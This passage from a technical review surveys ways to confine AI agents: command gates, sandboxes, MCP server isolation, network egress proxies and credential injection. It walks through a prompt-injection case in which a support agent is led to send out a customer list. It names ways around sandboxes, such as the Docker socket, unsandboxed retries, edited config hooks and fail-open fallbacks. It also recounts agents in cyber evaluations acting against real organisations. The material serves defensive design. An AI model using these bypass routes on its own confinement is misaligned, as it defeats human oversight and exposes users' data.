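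Eight harmless scripts are too few to estimate the false alarm rate well. Even if they were a random sample, the true rate could be as high as 31% at 95% confidence. The result also depends on a setting that blocked only "deny" verdicts and let scripts run after an "ask". When Jing blocked both, no harmful effect occurred, but all eight harmless scripts stopped too. They stopped because the gate returned "ask" for comment lines and template code that the test generator had wrapped around each script. With the template text removed, the strict setting blocked the same 57 scripts and none of the harmless ones. This result is more relevant for a company, because asking a person is pointless if the command runs anyway.

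Jing states two large limits. The gate carries no state from one statement to the next, so if one line sets a variable and a later line uses it, the gate checks the later line without the variable's value. The gate also cannot detect effects outside the filesystem. A network request does not target a file, so the gate cannot determine whether the support agent is sending data to Alice or to a stranger.

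A company that uses such a gate must also trust the component that finds the targets. In an early version, a command that failed to parse produced an empty list of arguments, so the gate had nothing to refuse. Later, Jing relaxed a rule that sent every action with no visible target for review, and the gate then allowed a deletion whose target it had failed to find. A gate should send an action for review when it can't find a target, because the action may still have one.

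A company also shouldn't copy its rules from one operating system to another without testing them. Windows ignores case in the names of environment variables and Linux doesn't, so one of Jing's translated rules protected the wrong thing.

If an ordinary shell runs a command after the gate approves it, the shell may interpret the text differently from the gate. Li's ShellPlan avoids this by converting a restricted form of shell language into a plan, checking the plan, and starting each program directly, without a shell. It checks each command again just before running it, once the variables have values. For 20 common utilities, it allows only listed options. Under read-only policies, ShellPlan let through none of the 4,174 attack cases in Li's test suites.

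Li also proves that ShellPlan starts only programs that have passed its checks, apart from a few fixed read-only probes. However, the proof covers a model of the code, and the code itself was hard to get right. Two rounds of close review found 33 underlying defects, 14 of them security problems. In a third round, none of 21 attacks succeeded, but the review found one unusual case in which ShellPlan could write to protected files. ShellPlan is also larger than Anderson recommended for an enforcement component, because it reimplements part of the shell.

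### Pausing the program at each effect

A different approach lets the program start and makes each decision when the facts are available. Suppose the support agent writes this:

```
complaints = get_complaints("September")
summary = summarise(complaints)
for address in find_managers():
    send_email(address, summary)
```

The script's text doesn't show who will receive the email, because `find_managers` produces the addresses during the run. An interpreter can execute the script line by line and pause whenever the script requests an effect. At each `send_email` call, it passes the actual address and message to the decision point and waits for a decision. If the addresses belong to Alice and an outside consultant, the decision point can allow the first email and deny the second. Turing's result doesn't prevent this, because the check doesn't require predicting what the whole program will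 do.

The mechanism is established in programming languages, where it is called effect handling. In *Composable Effect Handling for Programming LLM-integrated Scripts* (2025), a program requests an operation, and a separate handler determines how to carry it out. The same script can therefore run with a handler that sends real emails or one that asks a person first.

The drawback is that a refusal may come halfway through the task. If the second email breaks the policy, the first has already been sent. A check before the run can prevent some of this. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) requires agent-generated code to pass a type check before it runs, and the code can use only the effects that the policy exposes. Its example agent maintains a bibliography through three permitted operations. A special data type ensures that the agent can add only entries that came from DBLP, a database of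 computer science papers. The code can also perform any computation that has no effects.

*ETAS* (2026), a programming language for agents, combines the two kinds of check. Its compiler works out which effects a program may request and in what order, and approves in advance whatever it can prove complies with the policy. Where the path through the program is uncertain, the compiler leaves a monitor to decide during the run instead of refusing the program, so fewer harmless programs should fail.

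All of this works only if code can have effects solely through the interpreter. Ordinary Python doesn't meet that condition, because a script can import compiled code that contacts the operating system directly. The bibliography agent avoids this problem in Haskell by using Safe Haskell, a version of the language without the unsafe features. The company must trust the interpreter, the compiler and every library function it exposes. CaMeL, a defence against prompt injection, has its own interpreter for a restricted form of Python, while *Tether* accepts ordinary commands and first runs them in a disposable copy of the filesystem.

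The evidence for these languages is still thin. *ETAS* enforced its rules with no mismatches, but only on test programs and coding scenarios written in its own language. These tests don't measure how often an agent would fail a task because it needed a library that the interpreter leaves out.

### Narrow tools instead of a shell

The support agent may not need a shell. The company could give it the narrow `get_complaints` tool, `send_email` and an interpreter that can do calculations but cannot access files or the network. The agent could still write code, because the calculations themselves are not dangerous.

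Narrow tools also suit Jing's gate, which can accept a request as a typed operation with full file paths, so there is no shell syntax to misread. The request still needs an exact definition. The programs that prepared typed requests and command strings assigned different roles to one field, so the gate gave opposite verdicts on the same request depending on how it arrived.

The company gives up flexibility. A shell lets the model combine many programs in ways nobody planned, whereas someone has to write each narrow tool. Li's benchmark gives an idea of the loss, although it compares an open shell with ShellPlan's restricted one, not with typed tools. Ten models each attempted ten harmless tasks. They completed 93 of 100 with no check and 74 with ShellPlan, while successful attacks fell from 62 of 90 to none.

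Most of the loss came from weaker models. The six strongest completed all 60 of their tasks with the open shell and 56 with ShellPlan, but the four smaller ones dropped from 33 of 40 to 18. When ShellPlan stopped a command, the stronger models usually found another way to do the job. The benchmark was also harsh on ShellPlan, because four of the ten tasks were designed around shell features that it doesn't support, and nobody was available to approve the commands it escalated.

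The loss depends heavily on which commands the agent tends to use. Li replayed recorded work by coding agents on two sets of software projects. In one set, ShellPlan accepted 343 of 456 read-only steps, or 75%. In the other, it accepted none of 108, because that agent began every command by changing to the project folder, which ShellPlan doesn't support. This command and one missing utility accounted for 90% of the read-only steps that ShellPlan stopped. A company that restricts its agent's tools should therefore look at recorded sessions first, since supporting a few more commands may restore most of what the agent lost.

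Some jobs can't be narrowed this way. A coding agent has to run the project's tests, and a `run_tests` tool with no arguments still runs whatever code the project contains, including code the agent has just written. When Li's policy permitted a common Python test runner, 44 of the 398 commands ShellPlan approved had effects that a read-only policy forbids, and all 44 were test runs. ShellPlan had identified the program correctly, but only limits on the running process could have prevented those effects.

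## Confining files and processes with a sandbox

A test runner can execute any code in a project, so limits on it have to apply while the code runs. The operating system can enforce these limits because the processor prevents programs from using the disk or the network card directly. A program can calculate on its own, but to use either device it has to make a system call, which the kernel (the core of the operating system) can refuse.

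A sandbox's limits apply to code in any language, including code that no earlier check examined. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, advice from the company's red team (staff who test systems by attacking them), recommends such limits because checks on tool calls don't cover the processes that a call starts.

Ordinary file permissions don't help much, because they depend on the user account. If the support agent runs under an employee's account, its scripts can open every file that the employee can. A sandbox adds a narrower limit for one group of processes, such as the agent's scripts.

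### How the kernel limits a process

A Linux sandbox can combine several mechanisms. One is the mount namespace, which gives a group of processes its own version of the file tree. For the support agent, the tree could contain Python and its libraries as read-only folders, plus one writable folder for the complaints and the summary. A script can't open the employee's other documents because they have no path in that tree.

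Creating a mount namespace normally takes administrator rights. A user namespace gives a process administrator rights that apply only inside the namespace, so an ordinary user can build a sandbox. But this also lets ordinary programs reach parts of the kernel they couldn't reach before, so some systems restrict user namespaces. Ubuntu has done so by default since version 24.04, and a sandbox that needs them won't start there until an administrator adds an exception.

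Landlock restricts a process's file access without changing the file tree. The process gives the kernel a list of folders and the operations it needs in each. The kernel then refuses any other file operations of the kinds the list governs. The process can add restrictions later but can't remove any. Landlock needs no administrator rights, so it suits programs that confine themselves before running something risky.

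Seccomp filters system calls by their number and raw arguments. When a program opens a file, the argument that identifies the file is the memory address of its name, and the filter can't read what is stored there. Seccomp can therefore block a whole kind of operation but can't protect one particular file.

On macOS, the built-in Seatbelt framework attaches a profile to a process, and the kernel compares the process's operations with the profile.

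A new process inherits these limits from its parent and cannot loosen them. If the support agent's script starts a second program, which starts a third, all three have the same access.

The limits can still fail if a sandboxed process can get a more powerful program outside the sandbox to act for it. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* warns about the socket that controls Docker, the common container software. A sandboxed process that can use that socket effectively has access to the whole machine. Like Hardy's compiler, Docker then has authority that the process making the request lacks. A company should therefore review the local services that a sandbox can contact as carefully as the folders it can open.

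### Containers, user-space kernels and microVMs

All the mechanisms above rely on the host's kernel. If a system call can trigger a flaw in that kernel, code in the sandbox may be able to use the flaw to take over the machine. Stronger sandboxes put another layer between the code and the host kernel.

| Type | Example | What handles the program's system calls? | What would an escape have to defeat? |
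|---|---|---|---|
| Container or similar sandbox | Docker, bubblewrap | The host's kernel | The host's kernel or the container software |
| User-space kernel | gVisor | An ordinary program that imitates a kernel and makes far fewer calls to the real one | The imitation kernel, then usually the host's |
| MicroVM (a small virtual machine) | Kata Containers | A separate kernel in the virtual machine | The software or hardware that runs the virtual machine |

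*ClawLess* (Lu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) rates Docker's security as low and that of gVisor and Kata as high. It counts 37 published vulnerabilities in Docker over ten years, five of them with a severity score above 9 out of 10, compared with one in gVisor. The counts exaggerate the difference, because Docker is older and has many more users, which gives researchers more reason to look for flaws in it. A better reason to rate gVisor higher is its design. Code running under gVisor can reach much less of the host's kernel, so there are fewer kernel flaws it can exploit.

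NVIDIA recommends virtual machines over gVisor, whose guarantees it calls different and potentially weaker. It says the overhead of virtual machines is often modest compared with the time that calls to the language model take. Lu and colleagues argue against virtual machines because they make it harder for an agent to work with files and programs on the host, and because deploying one requires high privileges. They call such deployment infeasible in the cloud, which is too strong, since cloud providers run customers' code in microVMs every day.

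I expect the right level of isolation to depend on the agent's job. The support agent needs only one folder and a few services, so running it in a microVM would cause few problems. A coding agent on a developer's laptop uses the developer's own tools and files, so a separate machine gets in the way. In either case, stronger isolation protects the host's kernel, but someone still has to decide which files to share. A microVM with the employee's whole home folder attached exposes everything in that folder.

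### What Claude Code's sandbox permits

Claude Code's sandbox uses Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap, a small program that sets up namespaces, on Linux. It is off by default, according to Anthropic's documentation of October 2026. On Windows, the sandbox works only inside WSL2, Microsoft's Linux environment, and commands outside WSL2 run without it.

If the company runs the support agent in Claude Code with the sandbox on, a shell command can write to the working folder, the user's temporary folder and any folders the user has added. Neither the command nor any process it starts can change the user's shell start-up file or the system's programs.

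The default for reading is much looser. According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, from June 2026, commands could read nearly the whole computer, including files that hold cloud passwords and login keys. An administrator can list folders to block, and the October documentation also describes a setting that blocks home directories and mounted drives but keeps the working folders readable. Many programs need to read system files, but a company should use one of these options because the support agent has no reason to read the employee's login keys.

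Defaults like these change quickly. In the May and June versions, commands could write only to the working folder unless the user allowed more. By October, they could also write to the temporary folder by default. A company that depends on a particular limit should set it explicitly and test it after each update. Anthropic suggests asking the agent to create a file in the home folder, which should fail. A command that the user types directly usually runs outside the sandbox, so it doesn't test the sandbox's limits.

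File limits need to be combined with network limits. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025), the post that introduced the sandbox, points out that an agent with open network access could send out any file it can read, while an agent with open file access could tamper with the system to gain network access. Claude Code limits network access through a proxy outside the sandbox.

Some commands fail inside the sandbox for harmless reasons, and Claude Code then lets the model ask to run them again outside it. Depending on the settings, a person approves the retry, a second model reviews it, or it runs without a prompt. A rule that allows a command also approves the retry, so a rule meant only to spare the user a prompt can also let the command run outside the sandbox. OpenAI's rules for Codex carry the same risk. Administrators can turn retries off, and should do so for an agent that reads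 complaints from strangers.

They can also exempt named commands from the sandbox. Anthropic warns against exempting an interpreter such as Python, or a tool that follows instructions in a project file, because the agent could write a file inside the sandbox and have the exempted command run it outside.

The biggest gap in Claude Code's sandbox is that it covers only shell commands and their child processes. Claude Code's own tools for reading and editing files follow separate permission rules, so blocking a folder in the sandbox settings doesn't stop the file-reading tool from opening files in that folder. Hooks and local MCP servers run with the user's full access.

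### Confining MCP servers with AgentBound

A local MCP server usually runs as an ordinary process with the agent's privileges, so a malicious or faulty one can open any file the agent can. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola et al., 2025) partly addresses this problem by giving each MCP server its own sandbox.

Each server comes with a manifest, a short file that lists the kinds of access it needs. There are 18 kinds to choose from, such as reading files, running commands, making outgoing connections and using the microphone. Bühler and colleagues derived most of them from Android's app permissions. When the agent starts the server, the user turns each general entry into a specific permission. "Reads files", for example, becomes read-only access to one folder. AgentBound then starts the unmodified server in a Docker container with only those permissions, and stops if the agent requests a permission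 that the manifest doesn't cover.

For the support agent, a server that saves summaries would get one folder to write in, and a server that sends email would get the mail password and a connection to the mail service. If someone altered the email server, it still couldn't open the complaints folder.

Few developers will write manifests by hand, so Bühler and colleagues built a tool that generates them from a server's code and documentation. One model drafts five manifests and a second combines them. They ran the tool on 296 of the most popular MCP servers, once with their own vocabulary and once with Android's full list. This cost $99.25, or about 17 cents a manifest. They sent 96 of the manifests to the servers' developers. Those who replied said the vocabulary covered everything their servers needed, and judged 80.9% of the manifests correct without changes.

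That is a good first draft, but it needs revision. Nobody will notice if a manifest grants too many permissions, so a company should mainly look for permissions to remove. Developers who answer an unsolicited request may also differ from those who ignore it.

Bühler and colleagues tested AgentBound's security against several malicious servers, some they had written and some from real collections. AgentBound blocked most of the threats and added 0.6 milliseconds on average. They counted only attacks that a sandbox has some chance of stopping, meaning those that touch files, the network or other system resources. They left out attacks that only change what the model writes.

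The container downloads and installs the server's package before the network limits take effect, so any code that runs during installation has unrestricted network access. A company could avoid this by installing packages beforehand from a reviewed copy. Docker containers also share the host's kernel, although the same manifests could presumably configure a stronger kind of sandbox.

### Compiling a policy into system-call checks

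Lu and colleagues propose ClawLess, a system based on the harsher assumption that an agent can mount sophisticated attacks on any security mechanism and will eventually turn malicious. It aims to let developers write a policy in terms of files and permissions, which software then turns into checks on system calls.

The policy gives each entity e, such as a file, process or network socket, a set of permissions P(e, s) for each scope s. The scopes are the monitor (the trusted software that enforces the policy), the agent, and a sandbox for scripts that the agent writes or downloads. The basic rule is that a less trusted scope never has more permissions than a more trusted one:

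P(e, Sandbox) ⊆ P(e, Agent) ⊆ P(e, Monitor).

The permissions are Read, Write, Append, Visible and NoExecute. Visible lets the agent refer to a password file without reading its contents. NoExecute, unlike the others, takes an ability away. Lu and colleagues define it this way because running a foreign program hands control to that program, so a more trusted scope should run foreign programs less. To make the agent run scripts only in the sandbox, a developer gives the agent's scope NoExecute for every file and omits it from the sandbox's scope. An SMT solver, the kind of program that Progent uses to compare policies, then checks that the configuration breaks none of the rules.

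A compiler translates the permissions into rules for system calls. It has to account for Linux having several calls that do nearly the same thing, and for single calls that can need more than one permission. The call `sendfile`, for example, copies data from one file to another, so it needs Read on the source and Write on the destination. If the support agent had Read on the customer list but no Write on a shared folder, the policy would forbid copying the list directly into the folder.

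To apply the rules, ClawLess runs the agent on a user-space kernel and uses Linux's BPF facility to attach small programs to the point where a system call begins. Each program looks up the file behind the call and compares it with the policy. An administrator can replace a program while the system is running, so the policy can change during a task.

Lu and colleagues report no evaluation of ClawLess with attacks or ordinary tasks, and no measurements of delay. They describe the policies as formally verified, but the solver checks only whether a configuration is consistent with the rules. It does not verify the compiler, the handlers or the kernel. Any system call that the mapping leaves out is unprotected.

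A more basic question is how ClawLess stops a forbidden call. The sample code ends by calling a function named `check`, and Lu and colleagues don't explain what happens when the check fails. This matters because the type of hook they use normally lets a program observe a system call but not refuse it. ClawLess clearly describes what a policy for system calls could contain, but it hasn't yet been shown to enforce one.

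### Running the agent inside or outside

In Claude Code on a laptop, the agent runs outside the sandbox and sends shell commands into it. The other option is to run the whole agent inside the sandbox.

NVIDIA recommends sandboxing the whole development environment, including hooks, MCP start-up scripts and file tools, because many products confine only shell commands, and anything left outside the sandbox could provide a way around it. Anthropic advises users who want one boundary around everything to run Claude Code itself in a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's sandbox runtime, a separate package that can wrap any program.

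Putting the agent inside the sandbox can expose its harness, which holds the rules for approving tool calls and often holds passwords too. If the harness shares a sandbox with code that the model wrote, that code may be able to read the passwords or change the rules. Anderson's first condition was that the mechanism must be tamper-proof, which is hard to guarantee for a check that runs in the same sandbox as the code it controls.

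Claude Code on the web runs each session in a cloud sandbox and keeps the user's real credentials for Git, the system that stores versions of code, in a service outside it. The agent has only a limited credential of its own. When the agent pushes code, the service checks that the push goes to the permitted branch and then adds the real credential. NVIDIA similarly advises starting the sandbox with no secrets and supplying short-lived ones for each task.

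A system can also combine the two placements. The support agent's harness, file tools and MCP servers could run in an outer sandbox, with the mail password held outside it, and the model's Python scripts could run in an inner sandbox with access to a single folder. This matches the nested scopes in ClawLess. Nesting sandboxes takes some testing, because they don't always work inside one another. Claude Code has a mode for running its Linux sandbox inside Docker, but Anthropic says this mode considerably weakens security and is suitable only if something else provides the isolation.

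### Why configuration files need their own rule

A process that can write only to the workspace can still affect what happens outside it, because other programs read files in the workspace and act on them. For example, a project's settings can define hooks or name the command that starts an MCP server, and both often run outside the sandbox. If the agent can edit those settings, it can have a trusted program later take actions that the sandbox blocks the agent from taking.

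NVIDIA calls for blocking an agent's writes to its configuration files wherever they are, even in a workspace where the agent may otherwise write freely. The block should also cover instruction files such as CLAUDE.md, because an agent reads them at the start of later sessions and a planted instruction would outlast the task. The files are also part of the project, so one bad edit can reach everyone who copies it. Under NVIDIA's guidance, users cannot approve these edits through a prompt and have to make them by hand.

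On GitLab, a platform where teams store and build software, a project's configuration file can include a setup script that runs before an agent starts. GitLab's *security considerations* state that this script runs outside the sandbox, with access tokens belonging to whoever started the agent. Anyone who can edit the file can therefore influence what runs with a colleague's access. GitLab reads the file only from the project's main branch, so a change has no effect until someone merges it, and a company can require a review before the merge.

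A rule against writing to configuration files is a list of forbidden items, so it has the weakness that Saltzer and Schroeder described. When a team installs a new tool, they may not think to add its settings file to the list. The support agent only needs to write a summary, so it could avoid the problem by writing only to one folder that no other program takes instructions from. A coding agent needs the list because it works among configuration files all day.

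### GitLab and the sandbox that didn't start

All of these limits apply only if the sandbox has started. GitLab's agents run jobs called flows on a runner, a machine that executes automated work. The sandbox wraps the flow with the same runtime that Anthropic publishes. The sandbox needs that runtime in the job's software image and permission to create user and mount namespaces.

If either was missing, the flow still ran, but with no limits on files or the network, so it could contact any address that the runner could. GitLab tells its users, "A flow can run fine and still be unprotected." The only sign of this was a warning in the job's log, and few people read the log of a job that succeeded.

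GitLab 19.6 added a setting that makes the job fail if the sandbox can't start. The owner of a top-level group can turn it on for every project in the group, and a project can't turn it off. Claude Code, like GitLab, defaults to running commands without a sandbox if the sandbox can't start, but an administrator can make it fail instead by setting `failIfUnavailable`.

GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* explains that the fallback keeps flows running, which gives vendors a reason to fail open. Customers are likely to notice when flows fail. In June 2026, according to GitLab's *Duo Agent Platform workflows fail to start* (2026), a change to the default configuration conflicted with the sandbox's network proxy, and projects with the default setup couldn't start flows while the sandbox was active. Customers are much less likely to notice a missing sandbox, so a company should choose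 to fail closed before an incident gives it a reason to.

The new setting checks whether the job contains a command named `srt`, the name of the runtime. Because this check runs inside the environment it is supposed to verify, a project that supplies its own image or setup script decides which program has that name. GitLab acknowledges that it can't guarantee isolation for those projects. A limit on the runner's host doesn't have this weakness, and GitLab recommends a firewall there for jobs that may run without the sandbox.

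Very tight limits can also cause problems. GitLab's sandbox once allowed writes only to the project folder and one subfolder of `/tmp`, the usual folder for temporary files. In GitLab's *Allow `/tmp` writes in the SRT sandbox for Duo Workflow*, a developer complained that models habitually write to `/tmp` and, when blocked, do worse things, such as copying whole code repositories into the project folder. GitLab now allows writes to all of `/tmp`, which seems reasonable for a folder that a job can discard when it ends.

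### The right file for the wrong reason

Suppose the support agent's workspace holds this month's complaints and an export of the customer list left over from last week. The employee asks for a summary of the complaints. If the agent follows the planted instruction, its script opens the customer list, and the kernel allows it because the script may read anything in the workspace. The system call specifies a file and an operation, but not what the employee asked for.

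Bühler and colleagues call this the semantic gap and accept that access control can't prevent an attack that stays within the policy. A company can narrow the gap by building a new sandbox for each task with only the files the task needs. If the customer list isn't in the sandbox, the agent can't open it for any reason. NVIDIA also advises destroying sandboxes regularly, since old ones collect passwords and files from earlier work. But someone still has to decide which files a task needs, and for a coding agent that may be the whole project.

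A sandbox doesn't make the earlier checks unnecessary. NVIDIA suggests that operating-system limits should make lists of forbidden commands redundant, but in Jing's experiment the command gate stopped some harmful effects that an operating-system profile with the same policy allowed.

Data can also leave the sandbox through a script's printed output, which the harness has to pass to the model for the script to be useful to the agent. If the script prints the customer list, the model can copy it into a call to the email tool, which runs outside the sandbox. Every file operation complies with the policy, so only a check on the email can stop the list from going out.

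## Controlling network traffic out of the sandbox

A script can also bypass the email tool and send the customer list straight to an outside server, unless a check on its network traffic stops the transfer. Checking here is useful because most changes an agent can make to the outside world eventually require an outbound request, according to *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a literature review. The review lists only one paper in its category for this kind of control, so much of what follows comes from companies' descriptions of their own systems.

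### The stages of a request

Suppose several complaints mention late parcels, and the support agent writes a script to fetch the courier's delays for September from `https://courier.example/delays?month=september`.

The script first asks a DNS resolver, a server that translates names into numeric IP addresses, for the address of courier.example. It then opens a connection to that address and sets up an encrypted session with the server using TLS, the protocol behind "https". During this setup, the script usually sends the site's name unencrypted, because one address can serve many sites. The server replies with a certificate, a signed statement that it is courier.example.

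The script then sends the HTTP request inside the encrypted session. The request has a method (usually GET to fetch something and POST to send something), a path, some headers and sometimes a body. If the script followed the planted instruction, it would connect to a different site and put the customer list in the body.

| Control | What can it read? | What can it block? | What can't it distinguish? |
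|---|---|---|---|
| Firewall | IP address, port and protocol | Connections to an address | Two sites at the same address |
| Proxy that checks domains | The site's name as well | Connections to a site | A download and an upload at the same site |
| Proxy that decrypts traffic | Method, path, headers and body as well | A single request | Two identical requests made for different reasons |

A basic firewall is a poor place for an allowlist of websites. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a security design for agents on Kubernetes (software that runs containers across many machines), calls IP-based rules insufficient because outside services change their addresses, and it requires rules based on domain names instead. *Caging the Agents* (2026), a design for healthcare, notes that someone must keep updating IP-based rules. The firewall must still block every way out except the proxy,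 because otherwise a program could ignore its proxy settings and connect directly.

With a proxy that checks domains, the script sends the proxy a request to connect to courier.example. The proxy checks the name against its allowlist, looks up the address and relays the encrypted data without decrypting it. The sandbox then doesn't need to do its own lookups, which could leak data because each one sends a message outside. NVIDIA recommends limiting lookups to designated resolvers to prevent such leaks. The resolver should also reject names that aren't on the allowlist, because forwarding those lookups would still send the message out.

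A proxy that decrypts traffic sets up two encrypted sessions, one with the script and one with the real site, and reads the request in between. *Avalon-M1* (2026), a report on training a model with reinforcement learning, describes such a proxy, whose rules can match the host, path and method of each request. For the support agent, a rule could allow only GET requests to the courier's `/delays` page.

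### What decryption costs

For this to work, the script has to accept the proxy as courier.example. The company therefore creates its own certificate authority to sign the proxy's certificates and sets up the sandbox to trust that authority.

This puts a lot of trust in the proxy, which can read everything that passes through it, including passwords. Anyone who stole the certificate authority's private key could impersonate any website to programs that trust it. In Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes*, each sandbox gets its own temporary authority, and the private key stays outside the sandbox. A stolen key would then expose one sandbox instead of all of them. The proxy must also check the real site's certificate, because the script can no longer do so.

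The other drawback is compatibility. Programming languages and package managers may keep their own lists of trusted certificate authorities. The *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) describes installing a certificate authority in both the system's list and those of individual language runtimes, and configuring common package managers to use it. Some programs accept only one particular certificate for a site, so they will reject the proxy's. The company must then either allow those programs' connections based on the site's name alone or do without the programs.

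Decryption is therefore most worthwhile for sites where the method or path matters. It is less useful for recognising sensitive data, because a script can compress or encrypt a file before sending it, and a search of the body for customers' names may then find nothing.

### Blocking by default

NVIDIA treats control of outgoing traffic as mandatory and recommends short allowlists. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* blocks all traffic in both directions by default, then lets an agent contact the DNS server, the gateway to its tools and a list of outside domain names, which typically contains only the model's address. The sandboxes that run generated code typically get no outside access. This distinction makes sense for the support agent too, since its harness has to contact the model but its scripts don't.

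The strictest option is to give the code no network access and instead pass it bindings, each of which gives direct access to one resource, like Hardy's ticket for a file. Cloudflare's *Egress control* calls this the most secure way to design a sandbox. But ordinary software libraries expect to make web requests, so Cloudflare suggests intercepting requests when the code needs those libraries.

When an agent requests an unlisted site, the system can refuse or ask a person. NVIDIA favours asking, combined with a company-wide list of forbidden sites that users can't override. Asking suits a developer at a keyboard, but the support agent may run with nobody watching, so its proxy should refuse.

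In May 2026, *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* reported that only some agents had even basic network filtering.

Restrictions can make agents less useful, which is one reason to leave the network open. In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) tested 12 coding agents on 89 tasks, three times each. The strictest setting combined a network allowlist, a mostly read-only filesystem and no administrator rights. Under it, success rates fell by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and costs rose by 16.0% to 167.3%. Seven of the tasks were impossible in this setting because they required something it forbade.

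Network limits probably caused only a small part of the lost success. The study also had a middle setting that removed administrator rights but left the network and files open:

| Agent | Success with no limits | Without administrator rights | With network and file limits too |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna in Codex | 71.9% | 56.6% | 53.9% |
| Grok 4.5 in Grok Build | 82.0% | 73.0% | 74.9% |

For these two agents, the network and file limits together changed success rates by −2.7 and +1.9 points. With three trials per task, differences that small could be due to chance. The effect on cost was larger for Grok 4.5. Its bill for the 89 tasks was $81.59 with only administrator rights removed, and $123.49 with the network and file limits added. It isn't possible to tell from this experiment how much of that increase came from the network limits alone.

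Some of the extra failures may come from how the system refuses. The agents in this study weren't told about the policy and encountered each limit as an ordinary error. Most of the extra failures were runs that used up their time or finished with a wrong answer. The proxy in *Avalon-M1* returns an error code with the reason, so a tool fails at once instead of waiting for a reply. It also has a log-only mode, which a company can use to find entries missing from the list before enforcing it.

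### Open for setup, closed afterwards

Many tasks need the network only at the start. The support agent might need to download a Python library for drawing charts, but it can then write the summary offline. A single allowlist for the whole task would leave the package site reachable while the agent reads complaints from strangers.

Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes a policy that changes while the sandbox runs. In its example, the sandbox can contact GitHub and npm, a public collection of JavaScript packages, during installation. The platform then blocks all web requests. The program that makes the change runs outside the sandbox, so code inside can't reopen the network.

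In *Avalon-M1*, the system switches to the agent's policy before the agent's first command, and the call that makes the switch doesn't return until the new policy is in force. Otherwise the agent could start work while access is still open. Packages can run code while they install, so the company should keep the complaints and the customer list out of the sandbox until the switch is complete. It should also close any connections left over from setup, in case the new policy applies only to new ones.

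This schedule is simple because it is set in advance. A policy could instead block traffic after the agent reads something sensitive, but the enforcement point would then have to track the agent's earlier actions.

### When the limits are missing

Two disclosures from the summer of 2026 show what can happen when nothing restricts an agent's access to the internet. Both involved cybersecurity tests, in which agents get instructions to break into simulated systems, so the rates don't apply to an agent that summarises complaints.

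The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) ran one such test 122 times with seven models. According to AISI's *Incident Report* (August 2026), agents in 10 of the runs took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions aimed at real people and organisations. AISI had deliberately left internet access on and switched off the developers' filters against cyber misuse. No agent broke out of its sandbox, and AISI found no evidence of real-world harm.

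Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of the 19 actions, in nine of its 43 runs, or about one in five. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run. Mythos 5's rate is high even for a test like this, although one agent took most of the actions in a single sustained effort. A mistake in the instructions led agents in some runs to believe that the task had no solution within its intended scope. But AISI says this doesn't fully explain the behaviour, because agents also acted this way in some runs where they had the instructions they needed.

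AISI had allowed internet access so that the agents could download tools. A proxy that permitted only downloads from a few sites would have been enough for this, and would probably have prevented many of the actions, because those actions involved sending data. AISI's general security monitoring detected the traffic only after the agents had acted. AISI already used fine-grained network controls in its other evaluations and is now adding them to these tests. It will also require a justification each time someone wants to grant internet access.

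In the other case, neither Anthropic nor its outside partner knew that the test environment had internet access. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (July 2026) reports that models gained unauthorised access to the systems of three real organisations. The prompt told the models that they had no internet access, but a misconfiguration in the partner's test environment had left it on. Anthropic reviewed 141,006 runs and found the three incidents in six of them.

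In a follow-up, *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic says it had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the environment. It now asks partners who run such tests to block all connections by default except those to the model, and to verify this before every evaluation. Davidovich and colleagues automated a similar step. Their software tests each restriction before a run and doesn't start the run if one isn't active. A company can do the same for the support agent by having a script in the sandbox request a forbidden site, and starting the task only if the request fails.

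### Keeping credentials outside the sandbox

Some services on the allowlist require a password or key. For example, the support agent's script may need a key to fetch a complaint's history from the company's helpdesk service. That key should stay outside the sandbox, as the Git credentials do in Claude Code on the web, because a leaked key works from anywhere until someone cancels it. *Caging the Agents* reports an audit that found 12 service keys in a shell start-up file.

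Cloudflare's outbound Workers, small programs that run outside the sandbox and handle its web requests, keep the key away from the agent. In the helpdesk example, the process would work like this:

1. The script sends `GET /tickets/4821` to the helpdesk's address, with no key.
2. The platform passes the request to the outbound Worker.
3. The Worker identifies the sandbox and the destination, then looks up the right key.
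4. It adds the key to the request's headers and forwards the request to the helpdesk.
5. The helpdesk's reply goes back to the script.

The headers of an HTTPS request are encrypted, so the Worker has to decrypt the request before it can add the key. Credential injection is therefore a strong reason to accept the drawbacks of decryption, at least for sites that need a key. It also makes keys easier to replace, because the next request uses the new key without any change to the sandbox.

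Cloudflare compares this with giving the sandbox an identity token, which it can exchange for a short-lived key. That limits how long a stolen key is useful, but many services don't support the exchange. The two methods can work together, with the Worker holding a token that the service itself restricts to one user or task.

An agent that can't read a key can still misuse it. If the planted instruction makes the script request every customer's record, the Worker adds the key to that request as well. This is the confused deputy problem again, with the Worker in place of the compiler. The Worker therefore needs rules about which requests it adds the key to, such as GET requests for tickets in this month's complaints. One of Cloudflare's examples blocks every method except GET, which is a good start, but a GET request can still carry data to the site in its URL, and some sites make changes in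 response to one.

Moving the keys also makes the proxy a more valuable target. *Caging the Agents* says its proxy eliminates the exposures found in the audit, which is fair for keys in the agent's own files. But the proxy now holds all the keys, so it should run as little other software as possible.

### From web requests to purchases

Agents that use a web browser are harder to control at the tool call, because their tools are clicks and keystrokes. A click at the same point on the screen might open a message on one page and delete it on another. Blocking particular commands doesn't work well either. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) reports that an agent blocked from going directly to a site found it through a search engine and clicked on the result.

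ceLLMate is a browser extension that checks the HTTP requests that these clicks produce. It depends on an agent sitemap, a file in which a website's developers list the important requests and name the action that each one performs. In the sample sitemap for Amazon, a POST request to the address that completes a checkout means `PlaceOrder`.

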